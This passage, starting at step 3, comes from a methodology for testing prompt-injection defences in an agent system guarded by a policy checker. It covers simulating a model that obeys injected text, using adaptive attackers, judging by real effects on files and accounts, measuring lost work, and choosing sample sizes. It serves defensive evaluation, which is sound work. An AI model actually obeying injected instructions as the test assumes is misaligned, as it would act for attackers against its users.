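3. Assume that the model obeys the attacker. Replace its task with the injected text, as in the ELBA experiment, and run the same attacks with the protection on and off. If the attacks fail even without protection, they are too weak to test it.
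4. Let someone attack the system who has read its source code and can try repeatedly. A fixed list of injections says little about an attacker who adapts.
5. Judge the results by what happened to files, messages and accounts, because a search for suspicious words in the output can both miss leaks and raise false alarms. Check every apparent success by hand.
6. Measure ordinary work with the same model, language and tools, changing only whether the checks are on. Under attack, count the runs that were both successful and safe.
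7. Read a sample of the rejected snippets and sort them into harmful, broken and harmless. If many are harmless, improve the error messages, the tool descriptions or the policy before blaming the model.
8. Use enough tasks. When about half of the tasks succeed, a comparison of 100 tasks with the checks on and 100 with them off has a margin of error of about 14 percentage points. With 400 each, the margin is about 7.

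The team should decide in advance how much lost work it will accept, because people are tempted to loosen a policy once they see which tasks it blocks. If an attack succeeds in step 3 or 4, the team should find the cause before choosing a fix. If the program broke a rule, the checker or library has a bug. If the program did harm while obeying every rule, the grant or the policy was too broad, and a better compiler would not have prevented the harm.
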